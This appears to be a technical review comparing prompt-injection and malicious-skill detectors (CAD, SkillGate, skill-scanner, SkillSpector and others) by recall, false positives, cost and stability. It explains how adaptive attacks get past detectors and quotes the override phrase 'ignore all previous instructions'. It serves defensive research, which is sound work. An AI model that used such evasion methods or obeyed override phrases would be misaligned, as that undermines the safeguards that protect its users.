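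Deleting one sentence does less damage than rejecting a page, but a setup guide with a missing step can still mislead an agent. If an attacker's instruction shares a sentence with useful information, CAD has to delete or keep both. Because CAD looks for instructions that don't belong, it would probably miss an installation command that is normal except for a misspelled package name.

### Fixed and adaptive attacks

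Liu and colleagues tested CAD by placing it between an agent and the text the agent fetched. They used two benchmarks. AgentDojo has fairly short tasks in banking, messaging and travel, and AgentDyn has longer ones involving GitHub, online shopping and daily life. CAD's training examples resembled the AgentDojo tasks, so the AgentDyn results show how well it works on unfamiliar material.

Clean utility is the share of tasks the agent completes when there is no attack. The attack success rate is the share of attacks that achieve the attacker's goal. One set of tests used the same attack wording against every defence. In the other, a language model adapted each attack to the defence by rewriting it several times, using the result of each attempt to improve the next. The results below are for an agent running on GPT-4o-mini.

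| Defence | AgentDojo: clean utility | AgentDojo: fixed attacks succeed | AgentDojo: adaptive attacks succeed | AgentDyn: clean utility | AgentDyn: fixed attacks succeed | AgentDyn: adaptive attacks succeed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 65.8% | 59.6% | 52.5% | 46.7% | 50.0% | 35.1% |
| PromptGuard 2 | 62.6% | 56.1% | 49.7% | 36.7% | 48.4% | 35.6% |
| DataFilter | 64.2% | 12.8% | 33.8% | 40.0% | 22.4% | 31.8% |
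| PIGuard | 44.5% | 0.0% | 26.7% | 20.0% | 4.2% | 17.8% |
| DRIFT | 49.1% | 2.5% | 6.1% | 18.3% | 3.4% | 9.9% |
| CAD | 57.6% | 0.0% | 8.0% | 36.7% | 3.5% | 8.6% |

The researchers compared CAD with ten defences, including the trained detectors PromptGuard 2 and PIGuard, DataFilter, a language model trained to remove instructions from data, and DRIFT, which restricts what the agent can do. PIGuard stopped every fixed attack on AgentDojo, but more than a quarter of the adaptive ones succeeded. A detector tested only on fixed attacks may therefore be much weaker than its score suggests.

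Clean utility is an indirect measure of false positives, since a filter that deletes legitimate sentences makes tasks harder to complete. CAD lowered clean utility by about 8 percentage points on AgentDojo and 10 on AgentDyn. The AgentDojo figure is uncertain because results from four training runs gave a 95% confidence interval of almost 8 points either way.

The GitHub tasks are the closest to software documentation, and CAD did poorly on them. Clean utility fell from 65% to 50%, while the success rate of adaptive attacks fell only from 12.8% to 8.3%. Results with Gemini 2.5 Flash as the agent were broadly similar across the two benchmarks. Both agent models are old, and an agent that resists more injections on its own would gain less from such a filter.

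### Screening without a query

A service that screens documentation before indexing has no query q, because nobody has asked a question yet. The same passage may later help answer hundreds of questions, and it may look out of place in only a few of those answers.

Liu and colleagues tested a version of CAD that leaves out the query and another that keeps the query but leaves out the rest of the document. On AgentDojo, these changes made little difference. On AgentDyn, they mattered much more:

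| Version | Clean utility | Fixed attacks succeed | Adaptive attacks succeed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Full CAD | 36.7% | 3.5% | 8.6% |
| No query | 28.3% | 7.9% | 7.5% |
| No surrounding text | 16.7% | 2.8% | 4.9% |

Fewer attacks succeeded without the surrounding text, but only because the filter deleted so much that the agent could do little. The surrounding text therefore mattered more than the query. A documentation service has that text, as long as it screens the page before splitting it into chunks. It could also have a language model write likely questions about each page and use them in place of the query. The researchers generated queries this way for training, but did not test the method for screening.

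### Training on reworded attacks

An attacker can express the same instruction in many ways, so a classifier may miss wording that differs from its training examples. Adversarial training adds altered attacks to the training data. Liu and colleagues control the share of altered attacks with a number α between 0 and 1:

training loss = α × (loss on altered attacks) + (1 − α) × (loss on original examples)

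The loss measures how wrong the classifier's answers are, and training reduces it. The researchers altered attacks by having a language model paraphrase them or by slightly changing the numbers in their embeddings. The second method takes less computation, but the changed numbers may not correspond to any real sentence. The two methods gave similar results, though paraphrases usually preserved slightly more utility. The table shows the results for paraphrases against adaptive attacks that the classifier had not seen in training.

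| α | AgentDojo: clean utility | AgentDojo: adaptive attacks succeed | AgentDyn: clean utility | AgentDyn: adaptive attacks succeed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 57.6% | 8.0% | 36.7% | 8.6% |
| 0.005 | 57.1% | 6.6% | 26.7% | 8.3% |
| 0.01 | 50.5% | 3.8% | 26.1% | 6.5% |
| 0.05 | 41.7% | 0.0% | 3.3% | 1.6% |
| 0.1 | 24.6% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 1.2% |

At α = 0.1, the agent was almost completely safe from attacks on AgentDyn, but it couldn't complete any tasks. The paraphrases may not explain all of the drop in utility between the first two rows on AgentDyn. The detector at α = 0 had no extra training, so the extra training itself could have caused some of the drop.

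The best value of α depends on the material. In the banking tasks, α = 0.05 stopped all the adaptive attacks without reducing clean utility. In the GitHub tasks, the same value cut clean utility from 50% to 5%, and about 4% of attacks still succeeded. The researchers recommend setting α separately for each use, so a documentation service would need to set it using its own material. Documentation is full of legitimate instructions, and a classifier trained to flag every rewording of an instruction will delete many of them. The GitHub results suggest that the service may have to accept a small α.

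### Patterns first, then a judge

LLM judges are more flexible than classifiers of this kind, but running one on every item costs more. SkillGate, the detector by Yang, Fu and colleagues, limits the cost by using its 530 patterns to decide which skills the judge examines and which parts of them.

If no pattern matches, SkillGate allows the skill without consulting the judge. For each match, it cuts out the matching text with 500 characters on either side. It drops windows that largely repeat one another and joins up to 20 of the rest, with a limit of 8,000 characters in total. Then it adds the skill's name, file path and other metadata and sends everything to GPT-5.4 mini. The model returns a label and a confidence score from 0 to 1, which determine the default action:

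| Label | Confidence | Action |
|---|---|---|
| SAFE | Any | Allow |
| SUSPICIOUS | Below 0.5 | Warn |
| SUSPICIOUS | 0.5 or higher | Quarantine for human review |
| MALICIOUS | 0.7 or higher | Block |

The windows give the judge some of the context that a pattern lacks. For SDKMAN's installation command, they would probably include the heading above it and a sentence or two about the tool. The judge may also recognize the official address from its training data, but it can't do this for a project newer than that data.

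SkillGate runs on the developer's machine and by default intercepts `npx skills add`, the usual command for installing a skill. Users can also configure it to check content that arrives through MCP, so it could examine replies from a documentation service, but the researchers measured its accuracy only on skills.

### What the judge changes

The researchers ran the patterns without the judge and the judge without the patterns to measure how much each part contributes. They again used the 1,650 skills in SkillsBench, and they averaged results involving the judge over three runs.

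| Version | Recall | False-positive rate | F1 | Calls to the judge |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Patterns only | 90.0% | 27.1% | 0.391 | 0 |
| Judge only, full file | 80.4% | 1.76% | 0.813 | 1,650 |
| Patterns and judge, up to 5 windows | 76.2% | 1.31% | 0.806 | 540 |
| Patterns and judge, up to 20 windows | 76.9% | 1.13% | 0.817 | 540 |

Adding the judge to the patterns cut false positives from 406 to 17, a 96% reduction. The judge also rejected about 20 of the 135 correct detections (15%), which lowered recall from 90.0% to 76.9%. This is a good tradeoff for a hub where nearly all skills are benign, but SkillGate still missed almost a quarter of the malicious skills. A better judge could not have recovered 15 of those, because the patterns never flagged them for review.

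The full-file judge caught slightly more malicious skills than the windowed version, probably because some of the harmful text lay outside the windows. The researchers prefer the windowed version for its lower false-positive rate, but this advantage is uncertain. The windowed version's three runs produced 7, 24 and 20 false positives, or between 0.5% and 1.6% of the benign skills, and the full-file average of 1.76% is only slightly above that range. The runs took place over three weeks, and the provider may have updated the model in that time.

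SkillGate still saves a lot of money and time. It sent the judge about 699,000 tokens for the whole test set, 77% fewer than the 3.02 million needed to send full files. Part of the saving comes from skipping two-thirds of the skills and part from sending only windows. A documentation service would save less from the windows, because a chunk may be shorter than a single window, but it could still save by skipping chunks with no match.

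A skill that matched no pattern took about 0.14 seconds, one sent to the judge took 2.2 seconds, and the average was 0.8 seconds. These times suit a check at installation better than checks on repeated documentation lookups.

Changing the confidence threshold made little difference. Lowering it from 0.70 to 0.14 would have raised recall to 82.4% and the false-positive rate to only 1.33%. The researchers found the lower value by looking at the test results, so it may perform worse on other skills.

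SkillGate's tests also assume that the attacker doesn't know SkillGate is in use and hasn't seen its patterns, but all of its code, including the patterns, is public. Given how adaptive attacks affected PIGuard, the 76.9% recall is probably too optimistic for an attacker who has studied the detector.

### Adding findings or reviewing them

SkillGate flags a skill only if a pattern matches and the judge agrees, so the judge can remove the patterns' false positives but can't add any. The two hub detectors that also combine rules with a model combine them differently. Yang, Ying and colleagues tested both detectors with three models.

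Cisco's skill-scanner sends a skill's contents to a language model in one prompt and asks it to list security problems with a severity for each. The scanner adds the model's findings to those from its static rules. If both report the same problem, it keeps the higher severity. The model can't remove a static finding, even a false one, so adding the model can't lower the false-positive rate.

NVIDIA's SkillSpector has three specialized model analysers, which look for problems such as prompt injection or a mismatch between a skill's description and its behaviour. Another model pass then checks all the findings, including those from static rules, against the file and keeps only those it confirms with at least 0.6 confidence. Using models can raise or lower the false-positive rate, depending on whether they add more false alarms than they discard.

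| Detector | Model | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| skill-scanner | None | 36.1% | 12.0% |
| skill-scanner | Qwen3.6 | 95.1% | 17.8% |
| skill-scanner | DeepSeek-V4 | 94.1% | 17.6% |
| skill-scanner | GPT-5.4 | 88.1% | 16.6% |
| SkillSpector | None | 52.0% | 17.3% |
| SkillSpector | Qwen3.6 | 68.7% | 7.0% |
| SkillSpector | DeepSeek-V4 | 85.8% | 10.3% |
| SkillSpector | GPT-5.4 | 94.2% | 22.2% |

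Adding a model to skill-scanner was worthwhile despite the extra false positives because it more than doubled recall. However, only better rules can bring the false-positive rate below the original 12.0%. SkillSpector's model review can achieve a lower error rate than its rules alone, but the result depends on the model. Replacing Qwen3.6 with GPT-5.4 would more than triple the false-positive rate with the same rules.

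Cisco's skill-scanner also has an optional "meta-analyzer" meant to reduce false positives. The commands that Yang, Ying and colleagues list don't turn it on, so the figures above probably don't include its effect.

The same scanner can also give very different results in different studies. Yang, Fu and colleagues ran the same version of skill-scanner with GPT-5.4 mini and measured 18.0% recall and a 0.73% false-positive rate. They counted only findings rated CRITICAL, because that threshold gave the best F1 in their test. Yang, Ying and colleagues also counted HIGH findings and measured recall above 97% with every model on a sample of the same SkillsBench skills.

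The choice of threshold can't be the whole explanation. If GPT-5.4 mini had performed as well as the larger models, the HIGH threshold would have had an F1 of roughly 0.58 on the full set, compared with the 0.29 reported for CRITICAL, and Yang, Fu and colleagues would have chosen it. They attribute the poor recall to skill-scanner's dependence on severity ratings, but the other study got much better results with the same ratings, so the smaller model or some difference in setup is a more likely cause.

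### The judge's instructions

A judge's error rate also depends on its prompt. Yang, Ying and colleagues showed this with skill-vetter, a skill that guides a coding agent through a security review of another skill. They ran it in Claude Code and let the agent read and search files but not run code or use the web.

After studying the agent's mistakes, the researchers added two sets of instructions. One tells the agent to base a rejection on evidence in the skill, not on hypothetical misuse. The other tells it not to dismiss an attack it has already identified, for example because the skill contains written instructions but no code.

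False positives fell most with GPT-5.4 on 150 benign and 150 malicious skills that the researchers had not used in the analysis. The average number of benign skills it flagged fell from 66.3 to 8.7, and the number of malicious skills it missed fell from 10.7 to 6.3. False positives fell in eight of the nine combinations of model and dataset and stayed the same in the ninth.

The new prompt did not always catch more attacks. On a dataset from a different source, skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 missed about 109 of 154 malicious skills with the old instructions and about 114 with the new ones. Still, the reduction in the false-positive rate from 44% to 6% is larger than most of the differences between detectors, so differences between two judges' results may be mostly due to their prompts.

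### Different verdicts on the same text

Unlike a static rule, a language model may give different verdicts on the same text, because it chooses each token partly at random. Most services have a "temperature" setting that can be lowered to reduce this randomness, but small numerical differences can change the output even at zero. Yang, Ying and colleagues cite a report that skill-scanner changed its verdict on 14% of skills over five runs at temperature zero.

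They also ran four detectors three times each with Qwen3.6 and identical settings. The table shows the share of skills whose verdict changed between runs. The ranges cover seven datasets.

| Detector | Lowest share | Highest share |
|---|---|---|
| skill-scanner | 1.2% | 16.3% |
| skill-vetter | 2.5% | 33.3% |
| SkillSpector | 11.7% | 57.4% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | 11.2% | 64.3% |

All four detectors were least consistent on MalWild, the dataset in which the researchers had relabelled many supposedly malicious skills. It contains many borderline cases.

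Most of this instability did not show up in F1, which usually varied by less than 0.02 between runs. If a detector flags a different 5 of 100 harmless pages each time, its false-positive rate stays at 5%, but the owners of those pages would see their documentation disappear and return for no apparent reason.

Documentation services are especially prone to this problem because they refresh their content. Suppose a judge has a 20% chance of flagging a harmless chunk on each check. Over ten refreshes, the chance of at least one flag is 89%. Repeated checks also give harmful text more chances to pass.

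A service could store each verdict with the exact text and rerun the judge only when the text changes. This would make the results stable, but mistaken verdicts would also persist until the text changed. A majority vote of three runs would reduce the effect of chance but triple the compute. A service could limit the extra runs to chunks with confidence scores near the threshold.

### Running costs

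Yang, Ying and colleagues estimated each detector's average cost per skill at public API prices. The costs below are those averages multiplied by 1,000.

| Detector | Tokens per skill | 1,000 skills, Qwen3.6 | 1,000 skills, DeepSeek-V4 | 1,000 skills, GPT-5.4 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| skill-scanner | 8,200–11,300 | $0.40 | $1.27 | $30.72 |
| SkillSpector | 49,300–73,200 | $3.16 | $9.96 | $162.20 |
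| skill-vetter | 95,400–175,600 | $1.16 | $7.23 | $505.75 |
| AI-Infra-Guard | 169,500–306,200 | $4.66 | $16.60 | $553.04 |

skill-scanner uses the fewest tokens because it sends a single prompt. The others call the model several times. AI-Infra-Guard, for example, has an agent that explores the files, audits the code and then reviews its own findings.

Spending more did not produce better results. skill-vetter cost over 400 times as much with GPT-5.4 as with Qwen3.6 but had a lower F1 (0.879 compared with 0.943). Across all 12 combinations, higher token use went with slightly lower F1 scores, though the correlation is too weak to mean much. Processing times are harder to compare because the researchers ran Qwen3.6 and DeepSeek-V4 on their own hardware and used GPT-5.4 through an API.

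SkillGate uses much less compute. It sent the judge an average of about 420 tokens per skill, including the skills it skipped. At its average speed, it could check the 9,372 Next.js snippets one after another in about two hours, assuming that a third of them match a pattern, as a third of the skills did. Snippets are shorter than skills, so fewer should match, but many consist of the commands that the patterns are meant to detect.

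After training, CAD runs without a large language model. In the AgentDyn tests, the agent took only about 5% longer with CAD than without it. However, the computation grows quickly with the length of the text, because CAD encodes the text again for each sentence it removes. A page of 200 sentences requires 201 encodings of nearly the full page, plus 200 of single sentences.

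## Measured error rates and the legitimate material that gets flagged

The broadest test of skill detectors so far is the November 2026 study by Yang, Ying and colleagues, who also read the false alarms to find their causes. Two other studies tested some of the same detectors and got very different error rates. All three studies tested the detectors on skills, so their figures need some adjustment before they apply to documentation.

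### Six detectors on 1,477 skills

Four of the six are the open-source detectors that hubs run: skill-scanner, SkillSpector, AI-Infra-Guard and ClawHub's static rules, which the researchers call ClawHub-Mod. ClawHub offers its rules only as a service, so the researchers rebuilt the engine from its source code and checked that it reproduced ClawHub's published results for six skills. They added two community detectors, skillscan-security and skill-vetter, because these had beaten the hubs' scanners in other benchmarks. Each detector that uses a language model ran with Qwen3.6, DeepSeek-V4 and GPT-5.4 in turn.

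The skills came from seven datasets. (The paper's abstract gives a total of 1,147, apparently a slip for 1,477.)

| Dataset | Source of the malicious skills | Malicious | Benign |
|---|---|---|---|
| MalWild | Public hubs | 95 | 34 |
| MalSkillBench, wild part | Public hubs | 148 | 19 |
| MalSkillBench, synthetic part | Made for testing | 150 | 150 |
| SkillTrustBench | Made for testing | 150 | 150 |
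| SkillsBench | Made for testing | 150 | 150 |
| OASB | Made for testing | 93 | 68 |
| Skill-Inject | Made for testing | 100 | 20 |
| Total | | 886 | 591 |

The researchers checked the labels of skills from public hubs by hand, using the same test of intent and harm that cut MalWild's malicious skills from 157 to 95. Removing duplicates shrank MalSkillBench's wild part from 703 skills to 193, of which they confirmed 148 as malicious, reclassified 19 as benign and set aside 26. They kept the original labels for the synthetic datasets because the creators had built the attacks on purpose. They therefore checked only 53 of the 591 benign labels in advance, all for skills previously labelled malicious. When they later studied the missed attacks, they found six mislabelled skills, too few to change the results much.

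The table shows selected results in order of false-positive rate. A flag means a verdict that would block installation. AI-Infra-Guard gives a safety score instead of a verdict, so the researchers counted a score of 60 or less out of 100 as a flag.

| Detector | Model | Recall | Benign skills flagged | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ClawHub-Mod | None | 7.4% | 0 | 0% |
| skill-vetter | Qwen3.6 | 93.0% | 37 | 6.3% |
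| skill-vetter | DeepSeek-V4 | 92.4% | 42 | 7.1% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | DeepSeek-V4 | 79.8% | 43 | 7.3% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | GPT-5.4 | 86.1% | 50 | 8.5% |
| SkillSpector | DeepSeek-V4 | 85.8% | 61 | 10.3% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | Qwen3.6 | 87.5% | 80 | 13.6% |
| skill-scanner | Qwen3.6 | 95.1% | 105 | 17.8% |
| skill-vetter | GPT-5.4 | 94.6% | 182 | 30.8% |
| skillscan-security | None | 85.1% | 298 | 50.4% |

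ClawHub-Mod's lack of false positives is weak evidence of its accuracy on benign skills. The 150 benign skills in MalSkillBench's synthetic part come from ClawHub, so they had already passed the hub's screening, which includes these rules. ClawHub-Mod also misses 93% of malicious skills, and a detector that flags so little has few chances to flag benign skills by mistake.

skillscan-security's recall is slightly flattering too. It failed to finish on 53 skills, which the researchers left out of the rates, and the counts show that all 53 were malicious. Counting them as missed would lower its recall to 80.0%.

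skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 had the best F1 of any combination. Replacing the model with GPT-5.4 raised recall by less than two percentage points and made the false-positive rate almost five times as high. The revised prompt that later cut skill-vetter's false alarms helped most with this model, so GPT-5.4 was probably applying the original instructions too broadly.

The rates behind these averages also differ widely between datasets. The false-positive counts here are calculated from the recall and F1 that the study reports for each dataset. With Qwen3.6, skill-vetter flagged none of the 68 benign skills in OASB but 8 of the 34 in MalWild (24%). skill-scanner flagged 14 of those 34 (41%). The people who built MalWild had already mistaken these 34 harmless skills for malicious ones. A service that screens many such borderline cases should expect an error rate closer to the MalWild figures than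 to the average.

### Recall of 95% in one study and 18% in another

In the SkillGate paper, Yang, Fu and colleagues measured a recall of 18.0% for skill-scanner with a language model, compared with 95.1% in the table above. In *MalSkillBench*, Guo, Jia and colleagues (2026) tested the same scanner on their full dataset and found a recall of 92.7%.

| | Yang, Ying and colleagues | Yang, Fu and colleagues | Guo and colleagues |
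|---|---|---|---|
| Scanner version | 2.0.11 | 2.0.11 | Latest at the time |
| Model | Qwen3.6, DeepSeek-V4 or GPT-5.4 | GPT-5.4 mini | GPT-5.4 mini |
| Malicious skills | 886 | 150 | 3,944 |
| Benign skills | 591 | 1,500 | 4,000 |
| Recall with model | 88.1–95.1% | 18.0% | 92.7% |
| False-positive rate with model | 16.6–17.8% | 0.7% | 36.6% |

Neither the choice of skills nor the scanner version explains the low figure. Both teams ran the same version of skill-scanner on the same 150 malicious skills from SkillsBench, and in the other team's tests it caught over 97% of them.

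The smaller model is not a good explanation for the gap either, because Guo and colleagues also used GPT-5.4 mini. The stricter severity threshold in the SkillGate tests (CRITICAL instead of HIGH) isn't enough to explain it, because both teams also ran the scanner without a model, and the gap remains at the same threshold. At HIGH, the static rules in one study caught 10 of the 150 malicious skills and flagged 19 of 1,500 benign skills (1.3%). In the other, they caught 97 malicious skills and, judging by the F1 score, flagged 16 of 150 benign ones (11%).

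Static rules don't vary between runs, so the input or the settings must have differed. SkillsBench stores each skill as a database record, with the instructions in one field and any scripts in another. Yang, Ying and colleagues rebuilt the original folders from these records, including the separate script files. Yang, Fu and colleagues describe their test items as Markdown files averaging about 7,000 characters. If they gave the scanner only the instructions, it could not have found anything in the scripts. Yang, Ying and colleagues also switched on the optional data-flow analysis, which would have added findings in those scripts. Some of the model calls in the SkillGate tests also failed, but judging by the reported timings, this was probably a minor problem.

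Missing scripts are the most likely cause, but the papers don't give enough detail to confirm it. For now, the 18.0% and the 0.7% false-positive rate from the same runs are poor guides to how skill-scanner performs on complete skills. Taken at face value, the 0.7% would look like the best result for any detector that uses a model.

The other two studies report similar recall but different false-positive rates. Guo and colleagues took their 4,000 benign skills from the most downloaded ones on ClawHub, and Yang, Ying and colleagues drew 150 of theirs from this same collection. Without a language model, skill-scanner flagged about 10% of these skills in both studies. With one, it flagged 36.6% in one study, while the F1 scores in the other imply between 12% and 17%. AI-Infra-Guard shows the same pattern, with 15.5% in one study and roughly 5% to 12% in the other. The language model therefore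 probably causes the difference, and GPT-5.4 mini may raise more false alarms than the larger models.

Guo and colleagues also tested scanners that the other study left out. Sentry's skill scanner had the highest recall, 98.4%, and flagged 23.4% of the benign skills. VirusTotal flagged only 4 of the 4,000 benign skills, but ClawHub uses it to decide which skills to block, so most skills that VirusTotal flags would never have entered the benign set. Every detector in their study with a recall above 80% flagged at least 15% of the benign skills.

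### ClawHub's warnings

Yang, Ying and colleagues also collected ClawHub's published scan results for about 85,000 skills. SkillSpector reported at least one finding for 91.4% of them and a high-severity finding for 50.4%, and it recommended against installing 45.8%. AI-Infra-Guard reported at least one finding for 55.2% and a high-severity finding for 28.0%.

This last figure is not a false-positive rate, because nobody has established which of the 85,000 skills are harmless. Some of the warnings must be correct, but malicious skills can't account for most of them. Bitdefender estimated the malicious share at 17%, and Yang, Fu and colleagues cite a report that puts it at about 20%. Even if 20% of the whole hub were malicious and SkillSpector had caught every malicious skill, it would still warn against about 32% of the rest.

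Whether those warnings are errors depends on what a warning means. *ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc, Rivera and colleagues, 2026) describes SkillSpector's findings as "advisory risk signals, not accusations". Several of the researchers work for NVIDIA, which makes SkillSpector, and others for the OpenClaw Foundation, so they have an interest in this reading. It does fit their data, which cover 67,453 skills that ClawHub's automated review had sorted into clean, suspicious and malicious. SkillSpector flagged 75% of the 25,504 suspicious skills but only 14 of the 206 malicious ones, while VirusTotal flagged 150 of the malicious ones. SkillSpector evidently looks for skills that request a lot of power over the user's machine, and most malware on the hub gets caught for other reasons.

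The scanners' flags also rarely overlap. Of the skills that SkillSpector, VirusTotal or ClawHub's static rules flagged, 82% had a flag from only one of the three. All three flagged 468 skills, or 0.7% of the total. These comparisons don't show which scanner was right, because the review's verdicts came from a language model that was given the scanners' results. Koc and colleagues plan to add human labels.

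SkillSpector with a language model flagged at most 22.2% of the 591 benign test skills, less than half the share it advised against on ClawHub. Ordinary skills on ClawHub may be harder to judge than the test skills, or ClawHub may run the scanner with a different model or version.

### What triggered the false alarms

For each benign skill that a detector wrongly blocked, Yang, Ying and colleagues examined up to three of the findings responsible. They sorted 2,790 findings by cause:

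| Cause | Findings | Share | Example |
|---|---|---|---|
| Access to credentials or local data | 1,016 | 36% | A phone-call skill sends its API key to the company that issued it |
| Exploitable-code pattern | 522 | 19% | A rule mistakes a JavaScript function declaration for code that runs other code |
| Mismatch between description and behaviour | 345 | 12% | A scanner reports shell access as undeclared although the skill declares it |
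| Instruction-like text | 284 | 10% | A skill tells the agent to start the next phase without asking |
| Installer or remote code | 261 | 9% | SDKMAN's official installation command |
| Incomplete analysis | 175 | 6% | The scanner can't open part of the code |
| Objectionable content | 90 | 3% | A trading skill has no risk warning |
| Dependencies | 77 | 3% | A rule ignores the version number when it looks up vulnerabilities |
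| Hidden or obfuscated content | 20 | Under 1% | A zero-width space with nothing hidden behind it |

The shares describe findings, not skills. A skill that several detectors flagged counts several times, and skill-vetter alone supplied a quarter of the findings.

Of the credential findings, 47% concerned the normal use of a service, as in the phone-call example, and another 39% concerned local data, such as a skill reading its own configuration file. In these cases the detector correctly identified that the skill handles sensitive data, but did not check whose data it was or where it was going.

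Plain misreadings made up about 500 findings, or 18% of the total, a figure reached by adding up the relevant shares from each category. They include placeholders mistaken for real passwords, documentation examples mistaken for commands that run, and words such as "system" or "policy" that match a rule by coincidence. More careful patterns could remove many of these, but most of the other false alarms would remain.

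Many findings were accurate but did not justify a block. In 43% of the mismatch findings, the skill's description did differ from its behaviour, for instance because the author had exaggerated what the skill could do or asked for more permissions than it needed. The exploitable-code findings were usually weaker. Over half concerned operations that used only local input, such as the user's own files, and an attacker's input could have reached an unsafe operation in just 1%. Even those would have been vulnerabilities, which an honest author can create by accident.

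Snyk's medium-risk audit of a Context7 skill is a similar case. Snyk warned about text from outsiders (risk score 0.80) and about the skill's dependence on a remote address whose content can steer the agent (0.90). Both warnings would apply to any service that fetches documentation for an agent, and Snyk did not report an attack. Blocking the skill because of this audit would be a false positive.

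The causes also vary by detector. Credential access accounts for half of skillscan-security's findings, because its rules match any mention of a secret. Exploitable code accounts for half of AI-Infra-Guard's, because it looks for vulnerabilities as well as malicious intent. When SkillSpector runs with a language model, its largest category is mismatch between description and behaviour (40%), which one of its model calls is designed to detect. Two detectors with the same overall false-positive rate can therefore reject quite different material. For a service that indexes many guides to logging in and managing keys, rules like skillscan-security's pose the greatest risk of false positives.

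SkillGate's false alarms have a different main cause. Of its average of 17 per run, about 13 concerned Base64 text in code examples and API documentation. Many web services accept a username and password in this form, so their manuals contain lines like this one:

`Authorization: Basic dXNlcjpwYXNz`

The last part decodes to `user:pass`. In these cases SkillGate's judge found nothing in the excerpt it received that made the text clearly harmless.

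Only about seven benign skills triggered an alarm in all three of SkillGate's runs. Each run also flagged about ten others that were not flagged every time. Cisco's skill-scanner can optionally run the language model several times and keep only the findings that appear in a majority of runs. A similar filter could remove many of SkillGate's inconsistent alarms, but the seven consistent ones, about 0.5% of the benign skills, would remain.

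### Harmless text with trigger words

Injection detectors are especially prone to flagging harmless text because many words used in attacks also appear in ordinary instructions. A good test would deliberately include harmless texts that contain these words, but the available tests are small or indirect.

In 45% of the 284 findings about instruction-like text, the instruction served the skill's own task. One skill contained the sentence "do not ask the user for permission to proceed to phase 3", which told the agent to continue with a sequence of steps. The detector flagged it as an attempt to bypass the user's permission settings. In another 40%, a keyword or pattern had matched by coincidence. The remaining 15% concerned skills that an outside attacker could influence, for example because they follow comments on a proposed code change. Those findings resemble Snyk's warnings about Context7.

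The benchmark for *ctxsentry* includes 25 harmless texts, among them a security policy, setup notes that mention API keys, a heading that reads "System Requirements", and web page elements that are invisible on screen but help blind users. The tool flags none of them, but its developer added several during the tuning that cut its findings from 733 to 5, so it passes partly because the developer adjusted it to these texts. Both results come from the developer, and nobody seems to have repeated the test on another repository.

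Guo and colleagues took the opposite approach and ran existing tools on material they were not built for. They tested five scanners for malicious packages and six prompt-injection defences, including PromptGuard 2, on their 4,000 benign skills. The worst of the 11 tools flagged 3,979 of them. Skills are an especially unfair test for injection defences because they consist of instructions to an agent, which many of these defences are designed to detect. Reference documentation should cause fewer of these false alarms, except in manuals for agent software.

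ramimac.me's *Claude Code Skills Scanner Benchmark* shows what happens at the extreme. It ran eight scanners without language models and picked the five skills to which each gave the worst score, 35 different skills in all. None turned out to be malicious. An AI agent made these judgements, so a few could be wrong, but many of the cases are easy. Twelve of the 35 are security tools whose files list attack patterns in order to detect them. One scanner's entire top five consisted of such tools, including ClawVet. Another scanner looks for invisible characters, and four of its five worst cases contained only the invisible code that tells a device to display a symbol as a coloured emoji.

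The benchmark selected only the most extreme scores, so this figure is not a false-positive rate. Each score also adds up the severity of all findings, so long skills tend to score higher. The selection is still informative for a documentation service. One of the 35 skills, which contains OpenClaw's official documentation on configuration, authentication, deployment and command-line use, produced 1,876 findings. Another, for the SurrealDB database, produced 251, mostly because its thorough documentation includes many examples with credentials and network calls.

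### From skills to documentation

Some causes of false alarms should be at least as common in documentation as in skills. Manuals routinely cover access to credentials, the largest category, and installation commands. Documentation also contains more placeholders and sample code than most skills, which should cause more plain misreadings. The Base64 alarms already came from API documentation inside skills.

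Other causes should become less common. A chunk of documentation rarely declares permissions, so a detector will rarely flag a wrong declaration, and it usually contains fewer instructions for an agent. A chunk also lacks a stated purpose for a judge to compare it with, but the service could make up for this by sending the library's description and the page's title with each chunk.

Both skill-scanner and skill-vetter sometimes treat missing code as a reason to reject a skill. Nearly every chunk of documentation refers to code that it doesn't contain, so a service that kept this rule would reject much of its own index. Dropping the rule would avoid all false positives caused by missing code.

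Text length also affects the false-positive rate. If a skill is about as long as ten chunks, and each chunk has the same independent chance of causing an alarm, a false-positive rate of 6.3% per skill corresponds to about 0.65% per chunk. At that rate, screening would wrongly reject about 60 of the 9,372 snippets in the Next.js documentation, compared with 590 at 6.3% per chunk. The true number could fall outside this range because skills and documentation differ in many other ways.

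Kao and colleagues made the one direct measurement on documentation, but it doesn't narrow the range much. Their scanner for executable code flagged 90% of harmless installation files, whereas GPT-4o flagged none. Installation files are among the hardest documentation to judge, so 90% is probably close to the worst case for a fixed rule. GPT-4o's result suggests that a language model can do much better even on such files, though the sample was small and the attacker didn't try to adapt.

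The error rate will certainly vary within a service's collection. A page about sorting a table contains almost nothing that a detector looks for, but an administration guide may tell the reader to create an account with full privileges, store its key in a file, open a port and add a job that runs every night. These steps all resemble things malware does, and the guide would be useless without them. If a judge is told that the page belongs to a database manual, it should accept most of these steps, but a static rule can't use that information.

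Security manuals are even harder to screen because they have to quote real attacks. The public description of *ctxsentry* contains the phrase "ignore all previous instructions", a command that opens a reverse shell, and the names of several sites that data thieves use. A language model can usually distinguish a quotation from an instruction if it sees the whole page, but the two may look the same in a chunk that contains only the quoted attack. An attacker could also disguise a real injection as an example.

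An average false-positive rate would hide a high error rate on security material. Suppose that 2% of a service's harmless chunks concern security, and that the screener rejects half of them and 0.2% of everything else. The overall false-positive rate would be about 1.2%, which sounds acceptable, but developers who asked their agents about security would be missing half of the harmless security material.

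## Missed threats and what catching them would cost

A more lenient screener would reject less security material but might miss more attacks. How many more depends on why detectors miss attacks. Yang, Ying and colleagues looked for the causes by comparing the malicious content of each missed skill with the detector's reports and logs. They classified 3,178 misses, counting a skill once for each detector and model that missed it.

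### Attacks that static rules miss

Detectors using only static rules produced 1,935 of these misses:

| Cause | ClawHub-Mod | skillscan-security | skill-scanner | SkillSpector | Total |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| No matching rule | 628 | 54 | 277 | 161 | 1,120 |
| Harmful request in ordinary language | 174 | 38 | 149 | 121 | 482 |
| Finding graded too low to block | 10 | 27 | 134 | 139 | 310 |

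The other 23 were labelling errors or files that the detectors skipped. ClawHub-Mod, which misses almost everything, accounts for over half of the first row. Without it, the totals are 492, 308 and 300, so missing rules are a less dominant cause than they first appear.

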